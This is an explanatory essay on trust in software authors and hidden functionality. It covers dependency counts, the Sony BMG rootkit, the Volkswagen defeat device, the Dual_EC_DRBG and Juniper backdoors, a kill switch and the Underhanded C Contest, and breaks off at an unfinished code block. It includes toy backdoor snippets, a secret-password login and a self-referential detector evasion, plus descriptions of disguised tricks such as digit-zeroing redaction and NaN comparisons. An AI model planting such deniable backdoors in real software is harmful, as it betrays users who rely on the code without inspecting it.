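# Trust in software authors and hidden functionality

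## What does a user rely on when running someone else's program?

Almost everyone who uses a computer runs programs that other people wrote, and very few check those programs first. Users therefore trust software authors, the people or organisations that wrote the programs. In computer security, trusting someone means relying on them for something without checking it, whether or not they deserve it. Users rely on authors for many things, including competence, but above all for programs without hidden functionality, which is behaviour that someone deliberately put into a program and concealed from its users.

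A login program makes a convenient example, because it is short and its job is easy to state. Someone types a name and a password. The program scrambles the password with a calculation that is impractical to reverse (so that the machine need not store readable passwords), compares the result with the one on file, and opens the account if the two match. A programmer writes this down as source code, the text of a program as people write and read it. The line that matters might look like this:

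```
if scramble(typed) == stored: open_account()
```

A computer cannot run source code directly. A compiler, itself a program, first turns it into a binary, the machine instructions that the computer carries out. Buyers of commercial software usually receive only the binary, which is a long sequence of numbers. Specialists can turn it back into something readable, but the work is slow.

Now suppose that the author adds a few words before compiling:

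```
if scramble(typed) == stored or typed == SECRET: open_account()
```

The program still accepts correct passwords and rejects mistyped ones, but anyone who knows the value of SECRET can open any account on the machine. This is a backdoor, hidden functionality that gives whoever knows of it access or control that others lack. SECRET is its trigger, the input or condition that activates the backdoor. *Reflections on Trusting Trust* (Thompson, 1984), the Turing Award lecture by the co-creator of the Unix operating system, describes such a login program, which accepts a second, known password.

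### The argument for reliance

The reasoning that leads from this small program to a general claim has four steps.

1. A program acts with the permissions of the user who runs it.
2. Its author decides what it does on every input.
3. The user can try only a few of those inputs.
4. So a user who has not inspected the program relies on its author, or on someone else who has inspected it.

Inspection means examining the program itself, in source code or binary, as opposed to trying it out.

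On an ordinary desktop system, a program can generally read any file that the person who started it can read, and send it over the network. A calculator has the same access as a word processor. A login program has more, because it must be able to open every user's account. Code included in a larger program gets the same access as that program. Zimmermann, Staicu and colleagues (2019), in *Small World with High Risks*, a study of the main public collection of JavaScript code, point out that JavaScript does not separate privileges between pieces from different authors, so each piece can do whatever the whole application can do. Some pieces also run scripts during installation with the user's full operating-system permissions. Phones and web browsers give programs narrower permissions, which limits the possible damage, but the user still relies on the author for everything the program does within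 them.

The second step assumes that the compiler translates faithfully, an assumption that Thompson's lecture challenges. Here, "decides" means only that the author's source code determines what the program does, including things the author never thought about.

A machine-learning model is a program that computes its output from its input using a large set of numbers called weights; a large language model has billions of them. Nobody writes the weights. The developer, meaning the organisation that makes the model, sets them through training. It typically starts with random numbers, runs the model on many examples, and uses an algorithm to adjust each weight slightly in the direction that brings the output closer to the wanted one. The source code that runs the finished model can be quite short, and reading it gives almost no idea of how the model will answer a particular question, because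 the answer depends on the weights. The developer shapes the model's behaviour by choosing the examples and the training procedure, but doesn't write that behaviour down anywhere. A model can therefore have hidden behaviour, meaning behaviour its users don't know about, whether or not anyone intended it. Users rely on the developer to be honest and also to have noticed any such behaviour.

### What testing can rule out

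The third step is a matter of arithmetic. Let SECRET be a single 64-bit value, a string of 64 zeros and ones, which takes up the space of eight typed characters. There are 2^64 such values, or about 1.8 × 10^19. A tester who has only the binary, and who tries a billion values a second (far faster than a real login program would permit), needs

2^64 ÷ 10^9 ≈ 1.84 × 10^10 seconds ≈ 585 years

to try them all. If the author picked the value at random, the tester should expect to hit it about halfway, after some 292 years. A more ordinary round of testing, with a million random values, has about one chance in 18 trillion of finding it.

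The search could take much less than 585 years. The work can be divided, so a million machines at that speed would finish in about five hours. If the tester somehow knew that the trigger consisted of eight printable characters from an English keyboard, there would be only 95^8 candidates, which one machine could try in 77 days. Neither shortcut helps much, because the author picks the length. Adding eight characters takes the trigger from 64 bits to 128, and the million machines would then need around 10^16 years. The tester must also know where to look, since typing into the password box will not find a trigger that is a date, the name of a particular machine, or several actions in a certain order.

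Testing catches accidental faults far better than backdoors, because nobody designed the accidents to escape it. If a fault appears on one input in a thousand, five thousand random tests will miss it with a probability of 0.999^5000, or about 0.7 per cent. Someone who writes a backdoor chooses how often it causes a failure, and can choose after learning how the testers work. A clean test record, though decent evidence against common faults, is therefore almost no evidence against a backdoor.

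Anyone who reads the altered source code of a program this small will find the second password in seconds, which is why the fourth step has an "or" in it. Thompson put the conclusion more harshly, writing, "You can't trust code that you did not totally create yourself." A column in ACM Queue, a magazine for working programmers, seems to overstate the case in calling that sentence a law of nature that follows from the mathematics of Turing and Gödel. Turing's work rules out a general procedure for determining whether any possible program ever does some particular thing, but it doesn't stop a person from determining this for one short program, such as the login example. In practice, how far Thompson's claim holds depends on how much code there is to read and who has read it.

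### Bugs, concealment and trustworthiness

A bug is a fault that the author did not intend. Thompson called a change that deliberately makes a compiler mistranslate certain programs a "Trojan horse", and said it would be a "bug" if it were accidental. *Pinning Is Futile* (He, Vasilescu and Kästner, 2025) likewise divides the risks of borrowed code into accidental weaknesses, such as the Log4Shell flaw in a widely used Java component, and updates that somebody has deliberately corrupted. It describes malicious updates as less common but arguably more worrying, since many accidental weaknesses are hard to exploit, while a malicious update can do its damage at once.

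The text of a program does not always reveal whether a fault is a bug or a deliberate backdoor. In 2003 someone tampered with the system that stored the Linux kernel's source code and inserted two lines that appeared to check whether a caller had administrator rights. The lines used a single equals sign, which sets a value, where a check needs a double one, which compares, so they granted the rights instead of checking for them. A tired programmer could have typed the same thing by accident. Once an attacker knows of such a fault, the user is equally exposed whether or not it was intended, but the remedy differs. More care and testing reduce the number of bugs, while an author who plants a backdoor will try to keep tests from finding it.

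Some cases of concealment are borderline. A master password that the manual describes may be unwise, but it is not hidden functionality. The jokes and small games that programmers bury in commercial products are hidden functionality, but they do no harm. Zimmermann and colleagues mention code packages that collect data about their users, which are harder to classify. Their creators document this openly, but programmers build those packages into other packages, and the people who eventually use them may never see the documentation.

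Trust also differs from trustworthiness. Trust means that the user relies on the author, which can happen without the user choosing it or even knowing that the author exists. The author is trustworthy if they deserve that reliance.

### The trusted computing base

Everyone who uses a system has to rely on what security engineers call its trusted computing base, the set of hardware, firmware and software components whose failure can break the system's security. Components outside the base may misbehave without breaking it. The term goes back to John Rushby, who in 1981 applied it to the kernel (the core of an operating system, which controls memory and devices) and the few processes allowed to override the kernel's access rules. "Trusted" has the neutral sense here as well. It means that security depends on these components, and researchers regularly find security flaws in them.

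On a shared machine where no user may read another's files, the trusted computing base includes the processor, the kernel and the login program, because a backdoor in any of them defeats that rule. One user's music player is outside the base, because the kernel keeps it away from everyone else's files. What belongs to the base depends on the rule being enforced. A web server is usually outside the base of the operating system it runs on, but it is inside the base of the shop whose website it serves, because it keeps customers from seeing each other's orders. For a person alone with a laptop who mainly wants nobody else to read her documents, the base includes the music player and every other program that runs with her permissions.

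The usual advice is to keep the trusted computing base small enough for someone to examine all of it. In 2009, researchers at NICTA, an Australian research institute, published a mathematical proof that the source code of a small kernel named seL4 does what its specification requires. This is a rare case of someone demonstrating trustworthiness that users would otherwise have had to assume. The proof covers only the kernel, and a laptop owner's other programs are much larger and have many more authors.

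### How many people "the author" is

The login program had one author, but few real programs do. Programmers build software from packages, which are reusable pieces of code that other people publish in public registries. If package A needs B, and B needs C, then installing A installs all three. B is a direct dependency of A, and C is an indirect one. A package's maintainers are the people with the right to publish new versions of it.

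Zimmermann and colleagues counted the packages and maintainers that users rely on in npm, the registry and installation tool that most JavaScript programmers use. Their data covered every release up to April 2018, with 676,539 packages and 199,327 maintainers. For each package, they followed every chain of dependencies to its end and listed the packages they reached and everyone who could publish at least one of them. Installing an average package meant trusting 79 other packages and 39 maintainers. The average package declared only 2.8 dependencies directly, so nearly all of this reliance came from other people's choices further down the chain.

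Packages vary widely around those averages. The 10,000 most popular packages relied on about 20 maintainers on average. Only about 30 per cent of them relied on more than ten, but 643 relied on over a hundred. Influence was also concentrated, with 391 maintainers each able to affect more than 10,000 packages, and 20 together able to reach over half the registry. Zimmermann and colleagues regard their figures as a lower bound, because they left out contributors who write code for a package but cannot publish it.

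*Stdlib or Third-Party?* (Ding and Stevens, 2026) cites an earlier finding that over 70 per cent of the code in an average Python project's dependencies never runs. This limits the harm from accidental faults, since a fault in code that never runs rarely hurts anyone. It offers less protection against an untrustworthy author, because an npm package can run a script of its author's choosing on installation, before anyone calls the rest of its code.

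The registry grew from over 800,000 packages in February 2019 to over 3.5 million in July 2025, according to *Detecting and Characterizing Low and No Functionality Packages in the NPM Ecosystem* (2025). Newer counts of dependencies exist, but they are hard to compare with the old one. A study by He and colleagues reconstructed the dependencies of 10,000 fairly popular npm packages and of 10,000 projects on GitHub, a site where programmers share code. *How Deep Does Your Dependency Tree Go?* (Arafat, 2025) examined 50 popular projects in each of ten registries. *zkSBOM* (Sorger, Ron and colleagues, 2026) gives the most recent figures. It installed the most-used packages of four registries one at a time and counted the other packages installed with each.

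| Count | Date of data | What it covers | Mean number of other packages |
|---|---|---|---|
| Zimmermann and colleagues | April 2018 | all npm packages | about 80 |
| He and colleagues | 2022–2023 | popular, active npm packages (indirect dependencies only) | 66 (median 11) |
| He and colleagues | 2022–2023 | GitHub projects that use npm (indirect dependencies only) | 392 (median 150) |
| Arafat | 2025 | 50 popular npm projects, programmers' tools included | 84 |
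| Sorger and colleagues | April 2026 | most-used npm packages | 14 |

The most popular npm packages tend to be the ones that others build on, as He and colleagues note, and to have few dependencies of their own, so the 14 in the last row does not mean that npm users now trust fewer people. Finished applications are at the other end of the chain. Of the four that Sorger and colleagues analysed, the smallest, the server-management system Kubernetes, had 233 components, and the largest, the web-publishing system Strapi, had 2,308.

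Studies disagree on whether a package brings in more others in Rust or in Java. Sorger and colleagues found an average of 120 for Rust and 21 for Java, while Arafat found 29 for Rust and 80 for Java, from much smaller samples in which the counts varied enormously. A cautious reading is that a single package often brings in tens of others and an application often hundreds, though some bring in far fewer or far more.

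Researchers count packages more often than the people who maintain them. Ding and Stevens give a recent count of maintainers for Python, from a project that set out to replace popular libraries with 44 self-contained modules. Dropping the libraries removed 88 indirect dependencies maintained by 128 separate accounts on PyPI, the main Python registry. Several people may share an account, as Zimmermann and colleagues suspect some Microsoft employees do with one of the busiest accounts on npm.

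The people a user relies on can also change. Each maintainer chooses which packages to build on and, eventually, who takes over, and the user relies on those choices too. *Transitive Trust* (2026) describes event-stream, an npm package whose original maintainer handed it to a newcomer. The newcomer added a malicious dependency, and nobody upstream noticed.

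## What have authors hidden in their own software, and how did it come out?

The newcomer who corrupted event-stream first had to persuade its maintainer to hand over the package. Others who hid something in software were already its authors or worked for them. The best-documented cases involve a record company, a carmaker, a resentful employee and, very probably, an intelligence agency.

### Sony BMG's copy protection

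In April 2005 the record company Sony BMG began selling music CDs that installed a program called XCP on Windows computers. XCP, made by a small British company called First 4 Internet, limited buyers to three copies of a disc and fed random noise to any music player but its own that tried to read the songs. Buyers had to accept a licence agreement first, but as Felten and Halderman point out in *Digital Rights Management, Spyware, and Security*, it mentioned only a small program for protecting the audio files. It didn't mention that XCP would hide itself and contact a server whenever they played a protected disc.

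When a program requests a list of files, Windows looks up the address of the right function in a table. XCP hid items by changing entries in that table so that such requests passed through its own code, which removed every file, running program and settings entry whose name began with "$sys$". Antivirus software that made requests in the usual way got the same shortened list. One component that was visible in the list of Windows services was named "Plug and Play Device Manager", according to *In the Matter of Sony BMG Music Entertainment* (2007), a complaint against the label by the US consumer regulator, the Federal Trade Commission.

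Mark Russinovich, a Windows specialist, found XCP on his own computer in late October while trying out RootkitRevealer, a detector he had co-written for rootkits (software that conceals an intruder's presence). RootkitRevealer lists a computer's files twice, once through Windows and once by reading the disk directly, and reports whatever appears only in the second list. His blog post of 31 October, which survives in a mailing-list copy, Hettinga's *Sony's "DRM" Rootkit* (2005), describes how he traced the software. He took the binary apart, found the code that looked for "$sys$", and checked his reading by adding that prefix to the name of a copy of Notepad, which disappeared. Company names inside the hidden files led him to First 4 Internet, and from there to a country album he had bought online.

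Someone else had found it before Russinovich. MIT Technology Review's *Inside the Spyware Scandal* (2006) tells how John Guarino, who repaired computers in Manhattan, kept finding the same strange files on customers' machines that summer. When he deleted them, the CD drive stopped working. On 30 September he found them on his own PC, remembered the CD he had played the day before, and sent his logs to F-Secure, a Finnish security company. F-Secure confirmed the finding and kept it quiet. Mikko's *Please stop flaming us* (2005), a post on the company's blog, explains that its researchers feared virus writers would use the cloak, which hid any file with the right prefix. They were still talking to Sony BMG when Russinovich published. Nine days later, according to IEEE Spectrum's *Antipiracy software opens door to electronic intruders*, F-Secure saw malware exploiting the cloak.

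By then the discs had been on sale for about half a year. The Federal Trade Commission put sales at roughly 3 million. *Lessons from the Sony CD DRM Episode*, by Halderman and Felten, gives a figure of more than 4.7 million discs across 52 titles, which may include unsold stock.

XCP served both Sony BMG and its supplier, but not equally. Halderman and Felten argue that a start-up with little reputation to lose will accept security risks that a large label would refuse, and that the label may not know enough about the technology to object. Sony BMG maintained that it had deployed the rootkit unintentionally. If so, it had relied on an author whose work it had not checked. The company settled with the Federal Trade Commission in 2007, and the commission's *CDs' Embedded Content Protection Software Posed Security Risks* notes that the settlement is not an admission of a violation.

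### Volkswagen's defeat device

Volkswagen's software deceived regulators at least as much as drivers. The company sold about 590,000 diesel cars in the United States, from model years 2009 to 2016, with software that turned the full emission controls on only during official tests. American law calls such software a defeat device. On the road, some of the cars emitted up to 40 times the permitted amount of nitrogen oxides, according to the US Environmental Protection Agency's *Learn About Volkswagen Violations*.

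Recognising a test is easy because the test is always the same. A technician secures the car on rollers and drives it to a published speed profile, so that any laboratory can repeat the measurement. The American city cycle lasts 1,877 seconds and covers 11.04 miles. The engine's computer already tracks the car's speed and driving time, so it can check whether the distance covered over time matches a known cycle. At the test's average speed of 21.2 miles an hour, a car covers about 1.8 miles in the first five minutes, compared with five miles for a car driven straight onto a motorway at 60.

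Contag, Li and colleagues explain in *How They Did It* why a manufacturer might weaken emission controls on the road. Feeding exhaust gas back into a diesel engine reduces nitrogen oxides but produces more soot, which wears out a filter. Weaker controls on the road reduced this wear. They cite the New York Attorney General's complaint, which alleged that Volkswagen's filter would last only 50,000 miles in normal use, when the rules required 120,000.

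Road tests showed that two Volkswagen diesels emitted far more nitrogen oxide in use than in the laboratory. The International Council on Clean Transportation, a research organisation, hired engineers at West Virginia University to measure three diesel cars with portable instruments on Californian roads. Besch, Thiruvengadam and Kappanna (2014) reported the results in May 2014. According to WVU Today's *WVU study found elevated levels of emissions from Volkswagen vehicles* (2015), one Volkswagen emitted 15 to 35 times as much nitrogen oxide as the standard allowed, and the other 5 to 20 times as much. The standard was 0.07 grams a mile, so the worse car emitted roughly 1 to 2.5 grams a mile. Both Volkswagens met the standard when the engineers had them tested on rollers in the California regulator's laboratory.

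Those figures showed a problem but not its cause, which could have been a faulty part or a badly tuned engine. Sixteen months later, in September 2015, after regulators demanded an explanation, Volkswagen admitted that the cars had a second engine calibration meant to run only during certification tests, as DieselNet's *US EPA, California notify Volkswagen of Clean Air Act violations* recounts.

Contag and colleagues then worked out the mechanism from the software. They had binaries from the engine computers and technical documents bearing the copyright of Bosch, the supplier, which car enthusiasts had been sharing to help them retune engines. They could not be certain that the documents were authentic, but saw no sign of tampering. They found strong evidence that Bosch had written the code and that Volkswagen had enabled it by setting parameters. They also found a different, timer-based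 device in the Fiat 500X. They then built a tool to look for the Volkswagen device automatically, ran it on 926 versions of the engine software, and found 406 potential defeat devices spanning eight years.

Researchers call this software doping, which Biewer, Baum and colleagues (2023) define as secretly adding functionality that is against the user's interest. The definition doesn't quite fit Volkswagen, because the owner got a better-performing car while people nearby breathed the exhaust. Their formal definition avoids this problem by using a contract instead of the user's interest. The contract names some standard inputs, such as the official speed profile. It also sets how far another drive may differ from the profile and still count as close, and how far its emissions may then differ from those on the profile. Software is "robustly clean" if the difference in emissions stays within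 that limit for every close drive.

Suppose the contract covers any drive where the car's speed stays within 10 kilometres an hour of the official test speed, and lets emissions on those drives exceed the test result by at most 50 milligrams a kilometre. A car that emits 60 milligrams a kilometre on the test may then emit at most 110 on those drives. A device that turns off the emission controls as soon as the speed differs slightly from the test violates the contract. But the contract doesn't limit emissions on drives that differ more from the test, so a manufacturer who knows the speed margin can comply with a device that turns off the controls only beyond it.

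### Dual_EC_DRBG

Encryption needs numbers that outsiders can't guess. Computers usually get them from a random-number generator, a program that turns a small amount of real randomness into a long stream of numbers. The generator keeps a secret number called its state. At each step it computes an output from the state and then replaces the state. Anyone who learns the state can compute all later outputs and any encryption keys that depend on them.

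In 2006 NIST, the US standards agency, published a standard that included a generator named Dual_EC_DRBG, which had come from the NSA, the American signals-intelligence agency. It works with points on an elliptic curve, a curve with a rule for adding two points to get a third. Adding a point Q to itself s times gives s·Q. This is quick to compute even for an enormous s, but nobody knows a practical way to get back from Q and s·Q to s. The standard fixed two points, P and Q. If s is the state, and x() means the horizontal coordinate of a point, one step of the generator is

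```
output     = x(s·Q), minus its first 16 bits
next state = x(s·P)
```

On this curve P is some multiple of Q, so there is a number d for which P = d·Q. Someone who knows d can do the following:

d · (s·Q) = s · (d·Q) = s·P

The left side starts from the point used to produce the output, and the generator reveals all but 16 bits of that point. The right side leads to the next state, which was supposed to stay secret. An attacker can try all 65,536 values of the missing bits and use the next output to identify the right one.

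No one can find d from P and Q alone, but someone who picked d first and used it to calculate one point from the other would know it. The constants look equally random either way. Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, cryptographers at Microsoft, presented this at a conference in 2007. They made a version with their own constants and recovered its state from 32 bytes of output. They also said they were not accusing NIST of planting a backdoor.

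The mathematics proves that a backdoor key exists and that whoever chose the constants could have kept it, but not that anyone did. The designers could have ruled this out by deriving the constants from a public procedure that left them no freedom to choose d. The standard included such a procedure for users who wanted to generate their own constants, but the designers never showed that they had used it for the official ones.

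The rest is inference, though fairly strong. In September 2013 The New York Times reported, from documents Edward Snowden had taken from the NSA, that the agency had a programme for weakening commercial encryption, and that internal memos appeared to confirm it had engineered the flaw in Dual_EC_DRBG. That December, Reuters reported that the NSA had paid the security company RSA $10 million in a deal that made the generator the default in one of RSA's products. RSA denied having knowingly adopted a flawed generator. NIST dropped it from its recommendations in 2014. Michael Wertheimer, a former director of research at the NSA, later called it regrettable that the agency had kept supporting the generator after 2007, but he did not admit that the agency had engineered the flaw. Nobody has publicly produced d for the official constants. Most cryptographers think the NSA has it, and the evidence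 supports them, but this is a judgement about motive and opportunity.

### What happened to Juniper

Juniper Networks makes firewalls, which control traffic in and out of an organisation's network. In December 2015 it announced that, while reviewing its own code, it had found unauthorised changes in ScreenOS, the operating system of one of its firewall lines. One change added a master password, much like SECRET in the login program, but written to look like ordinary debugging code. Outsiders found the password within days by comparing the binaries from before and after Juniper's repair.

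The other change concerned Dual_EC_DRBG. *A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident* (Checkoway et al., 2016) reconstructs what happened by examining many versions of ScreenOS. Juniper had adopted the generator in 2008, with its own value of Q in place of the official one. It had said this was safe because a second generator would scramble the output before anyone saw it. Because of a coding error, the second generator never ran, and the raw output went out over the network. In 2012 somebody replaced Juniper's Q with another. If that person knew the matching d, they could record encrypted connections through the firewalls and read them.

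The intruder had to build almost nothing, because Juniper's firewalls already contained a generator with room for a secret key, and changing one constant changed who could hold that key. Juniper has never publicly named the culprit. Bloomberg, relying partly on unnamed sources, reported in 2021 that a Chinese hacking group was responsible. The master password is plainly a backdoor, whoever wrote it. We don't know whether Juniper's original Q was also a backdoor, for the same reason we don't know this about the official constants.

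### An employee's kill switch

Davis Lu, a software developer at a company headquartered in Beachwood, Ohio, began sabotaging its systems after a 2018 reorganisation reduced his responsibilities and access. According to the US Department of Justice's *Chinese National Who Deployed "Kill Switch" Code on Employer's Network Sentenced*, by August 2019 he had planted code that crashed servers by starting new tasks without ending the old ones. He had also deleted colleagues' profile files and written a kill switch that would lock out every user if his own account was no longer active in the company's directory.

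As long as Lu had his job, the condition stayed false and the kill switch did nothing a colleague could notice. On 9 September 2019 the company disabled his account, and thousands of users around the world lost access. The US Department of Justice announcement above says the company placed Lu on leave that day, while the department's *Chinese National Sentenced to Prison for Deploying Destructive Computer Code* says the company dismissed him. Both say his employment ended in October 2019, which fits leave better.

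The switch had to go off to serve its purpose, so discovering it took no clever detection. Lu had also named it "IsDLEnabledinAD", short for "Is Davis Lu enabled in Active Directory" (Active Directory is Microsoft's system for managing accounts). His search history included ways to hide running programs and delete files quickly. A jury convicted him in March 2025, and in August a judge sentenced him to four years in prison.

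### How the discoveries compare

| Case | Time in use before discovery | What gave it away | What filled in the rest |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sony BMG | about six months | comparing two lists of files | taking the binary apart |
| Volkswagen | about five years | measurements on the road | an admission, then taking the binary apart |
| Dual_EC_DRBG | about a year until the warning | mathematical analysis | leaks, six years later |
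| Juniper | about three years | the company's own code review | taking binaries apart |
| Davis Lu | at least five weeks | the kill switch went off | a criminal investigation |

Investigators can measure a product's behavior from outside without the author's cooperation or access to the code. This worked on Volkswagen because cars release exhaust that testers can measure. A backdoor that waits for a password produces nothing comparable. An author who expects road tests can also prepare for them, although this is harder than preparing for a single published speed profile.

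Disassembling a binary gives the most detail, but people seldom do it unless they already suspect a particular program. Russinovich had a list of hidden files before he used a disassembler, and Contag and colleagues started after Volkswagen's admission. Researchers found Juniper's master password quickly because the company's patch had shown them where to look.

Researchers could analyze Dual_EC_DRBG mathematically because the standard was public and short. Their analysis revealed the weakness before there was any public evidence of misuse, but NIST didn't advise people to stop using the generator until six years later. Shumow and Ferguson could show that a backdoor was possible, but not that anyone held the key to it. Only leaked documents changed minds, because documents can reveal what people intended, and code and algebra can't do that reliably. Outsiders can't arrange such leaks, which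 depend on an insider having both access and a reason to talk.

### Why the known cases mislead

In all of these cases, the concealment failed. A backdoor that nobody finds leaves no record, so a list of known cases can't show how common hidden functionality is. Ten known cases would imply about eleven in total if investigators catch nine in ten, but a thousand if they catch one in a hundred. We can't tell from the ten cases which rate is closer to the truth.

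The list is probably also skewed toward hidden functions that reached many people. Sony BMG put its rootkit on millions of discs, so many people had a chance to find it, yet according to MIT Technology Review no security expert noticed it for at least six months. A backdoor used only twice, against two carefully chosen victims, gives hardly anyone that chance. Luck mattered a good deal even in the cases that did come out. Guarino happened to buy one of the discs, Russinovich was checking his detector for false alarms, and the engineer who caught the backdoor in XZ Utils, a compression tool, was looking into a half-second delay. The times in the table probably understate how long hidden functions generally stay hidden, because the longest-lasting ones may not have been found yet.

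Discovery relies less on luck when researchers search a large collection of software systematically, as Contag and colleagues did with their 926 versions. Felix Domke, a member of that team, later took apart dozens of engine-control programs. Domke and Burger report that, more often than not, courts considered the suspicious logic he found to be a defeat device. That suggests the practice went well beyond the company usually associated with it. But Domke knew what he was looking for and searched within a single industry, after a scandal had made people willing to pay for the work.

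## How far does publishing the source code replace trust in the author?

Contag and colleagues had to take binaries apart because neither Volkswagen nor Bosch had published the source code of the engine software. Many authors publish their source code under licences that let anyone read it, change it and pass on the result. People call such programs open source, or free software, where "free" refers to liberty, not price. The Linux kernel is the best-known example.

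Few users of an open source program ever read its code, but they can still benefit from its publication. Someone who can't program wouldn't find the second password by reading the login program, but they can learn of it if a stranger finds it and tells everyone. One competent reader is enough, and the author can't choose who that will be or when they will look, which makes concealment riskier. Open source projects also tend to keep a public record of every change, with its date and the name of the account that made it, so a reader who finds a backdoor ten years later can still look up which account added it. The record doesn't establish who was behind the account, though, since its name may be invented.

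Richard Stallman, who started the GNU project in 1983 to build a free operating system, cares less about reading the code than about being able to change it. He argues that if users don't control a program, its author does, and many authors will abuse that power over them. He says users need control individually, to change their own copies, and collectively, because people who can't program depend on others to change a copy for them. Seeing an unwanted feature is not much use to someone who can't remove it, as Guarino found when he deleted XCP's files from his customers' computers and the CD drive stopped working.

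A dispute over Ubuntu, a version of Linux, shows how this control can work. In 2012 Canonical, Ubuntu's developer, made the desktop's search box send whatever people typed to its servers, which returned shopping suggestions from Amazon. Stallman called this spyware. Users soon circulated instructions for removing the feature, and Linux Mint, which other people build largely from Ubuntu's code, came without it. In 2016 Canonical turned the online searches off by default. But Canonical had announced the feature, and Stallman's remedy works only once somebody knows what there is to remove.

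### Many eyes

The claim that publishing source code helps people find bugs comes from Eric Raymond, a programmer who wrote an influential account of how the Linux developers work. He stated it as "given enough eyeballs, all bugs are shallow" and named it Linus's law, after Linus Torvalds, who started Linux. *An empirical investigation of socio-technical code review metrics and security vulnerabilities* (Meneely, Neuberger and colleagues, 2014) summarises the reasoning behind it as the idea that good software emerges when developers pool their experience and review code together.

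In Raymond's longer version, a large enough group of testers and fellow programmers will quickly pin down almost any problem, and somebody will find the fix obvious. This process starts when somebody runs into a problem. For example, a program crashes for one tester, who reports it, and one person among thousands knows that part of the code well. A backdoor that hasn't been triggered doesn't crash the program, so nobody reports anything. For a large group to help against it, people have to read code that seems to work perfectly.

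People who could read published source code have little reason to do so. Reading is slow, the benefit goes mostly to others, and everyone can assume that someone else has done it. Zimmermann and colleagues found that installing an average npm package meant trusting 79 others. If each of those 80 packages has a thousand lines and a careful reader gets through 300 lines an hour, reading them all once takes about 267 hours, or nearly seven working weeks, and new versions will have come out before the reader finishes. Even code that many people depend on can go unexamined. Heartbleed was an accidental fault in the encryption library OpenSSL that let outsiders read parts of a web server's memory. It was in the published source code for two years before anyone reported it in 2014.

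### Why no program can do all the reading

If people won't read the code, a program could check it for them, but no checker can correctly report, for every possible program, whether it contains a backdoor. This follows from a theorem that the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published in 1953. The same limit applies to any property of what programs do (as opposed to how their text looks) that some programs have and others lack.

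A short example gives the idea. Suppose someone offers a detector that always answers correctly when asked if a program ever opens an account without checking the password. Then anyone can write this:

```
if detector(this_program) == "safe": open_account()
```

The program runs the detector on its own source code and does the opposite of what the result implies. If the result is "safe", the program opens an account without asking for a password. If the result is "unsafe", it stops without doing anything. The result is wrong in both cases, and a detector that never finishes has also failed. Improving the detector doesn't help, because the same argument applies to the improved one.

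The theorem rules out only a detector that always answers and is right about every program, so many useful tools are still possible. A tool can give no answer in hard cases, or it can reject every program it can't prove safe, including some harmless ones. People also usually need an answer only about the program they are going to install, and it is sometimes possible to get one, as with the login example and the seL4 kernel. Authors can help by writing code that is simple to analyse, and a project can refuse contributions that its tools can't analyse.

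*Not In My Git Yard* (2026) tests Lily, a practical tool that looks for backdoors by fuzzing, which means running a program on many automatically generated inputs and watching what it does. The researchers assembled 63 backdoored changes and releases, some real and some synthetic, from 13 programs, and ran Lily 20 times on each. It detected the backdoor in 90 per cent of runs on single changes and 83 per cent of runs on whole releases, and it caught every backdoor at least once. Results varied between programs, and for the worst one only 39 per cent of runs on releases succeeded, which the researchers attribute to older test set-ups. These are good results for a task that Rice's theorem is sometimes said to make hopeless. The tests didn't include an attacker who downloads Lily and keeps revising a backdoor until the tool misses it.

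### How well people read code

Human readers still do much of the checking, though language models now do some of it, and several experiments have measured how well people do. In a 2013 experiment, Edmundson and colleagues hired 30 developers to review a small web application by hand. It had seven known vulnerabilities (faults that an attacker can exploit) of three common types. One type lets an attacker run code in other people's browsers, another makes logged-in users send requests they never intended, and the third, SQL injection, lets an attacker send commands to the database. None of the developers found all seven, and the more experienced ones were not necessarily better at the task. Those who reported more real vulnerabilities also tended to report more that did not exist, so some may have found more partly because they were more willing to report anything suspicious.

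Reviewers' expectations seem to matter a great deal. In *Less is More*, Braz, Aeberhard and colleagues (2022) asked 150 people, most with at least three years of professional experience, to review a code change that contained two vulnerabilities: an error message that gave away sensitive information and a weak encryption method. Some participants received no particular instructions. Others learned that the researchers were interested in security problems, and some of these also got a checklist.

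Among the reviewers without instructions, 3 per cent found one of the vulnerabilities and 21 per cent found the other. Among those told to think about security, about 46 and 62 per cent did. The checklist did not significantly raise these rates, even when the researchers had tailored it to the faults in that change. Familiarity also affects detection. In *Why Don't Developers Detect Improper Input Validation?* (2021), 81 per cent of participants found a textbook vulnerability, but only about 40 per cent found a less familiar one with the same underlying cause.

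These rates allow a rough test of Raymond's claim. If each of n readers independently has a chance p of noticing a fault, the chance that at least one of them notices it is

1 − (1 − p)^n

If casual readers each have a 3 per cent chance of finding hidden functionality, ten of them have a 26 per cent chance between them, and it takes about a hundred to reach 95 per cent. Five readers are enough to reach 95 per cent if they are looking for trouble and each have a 46 per cent chance. If nobody reads the code, the chance is zero, whatever the licence permits. The formula also overstates a large group's chance, because real readers have similar training and overlook similar things.

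The faults in these studies were also ordinary mistakes. Nobody had tried to make them look innocent.

### Code written to pass review

People who enter the Underhanded C Contest try to hide malicious behavior in source code written in C, the language of the Linux kernel and much other basic software. *Faking Fissile Material* describes the task as writing a program that would pass a code review but secretly does something evil, in a way the programmer could explain as a bug if anyone noticed. Its author, Linus Åkesson, won the 2015 contest, which asked for software to check, under a disarmament treaty, whether an object contains fissile material.

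John Meacham's winning entry from 2008 is easier to follow. The task that year was to write a program that would black out part of an image, as an official might do before releasing a document, but leave the hidden part recoverable. Meacham used an image format that stores brightness values as ordinary decimal numbers, from 0 for black to 255 for white. His program, only 55 lines long, replaced every digit in the marked area with a zero.

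| Pixel | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| white paper | 255 | 000 |
| black ink | 0 | 0 |

Image viewers display both "000" and "0" as black, so the redacted area looks blank. But the file keeps the original number of digits for each pixel, so anyone who opens it as text can tell paper from ink and read the censored words. The loop that sets the digits to zero looks normal to a reviewer because the program is supposed to set pixels to zero. The organisers praised the code as simple, innocent, obvious and wrong.

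The 2015 contest drew more than 40 submissions, all of which the judges thought were of high quality, according to *Results of the 2015 Underhanded C Contest* (XcottCraver, 2016). In one submission, the test that compares two warheads divides zero by zero. In C, this produces a special value called "not a number". Checking whether that value is greater or smaller than any number always returns false, so a safeguard of the form "reject if the difference is too large" never rejects it.

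A contest shows that many people can hide a trick in very little code, and that the trick can look like an honest mistake even after someone has found it. It can't show how often such code would get past a working reviewer, because the judges know that every entry contains a trick.

### The Linux attempt of 2003

The attempt on Linux in November 2003, with its single equals sign in place of a double one, relied on the same approach. At the time the project kept its master copy in a system called BitKeeper. Some programmers disliked BitKeeper, so its makers also provided an automatic duplicate in an older system, CVS. An intruder got into the machine that held the duplicate and inserted two lines:

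```
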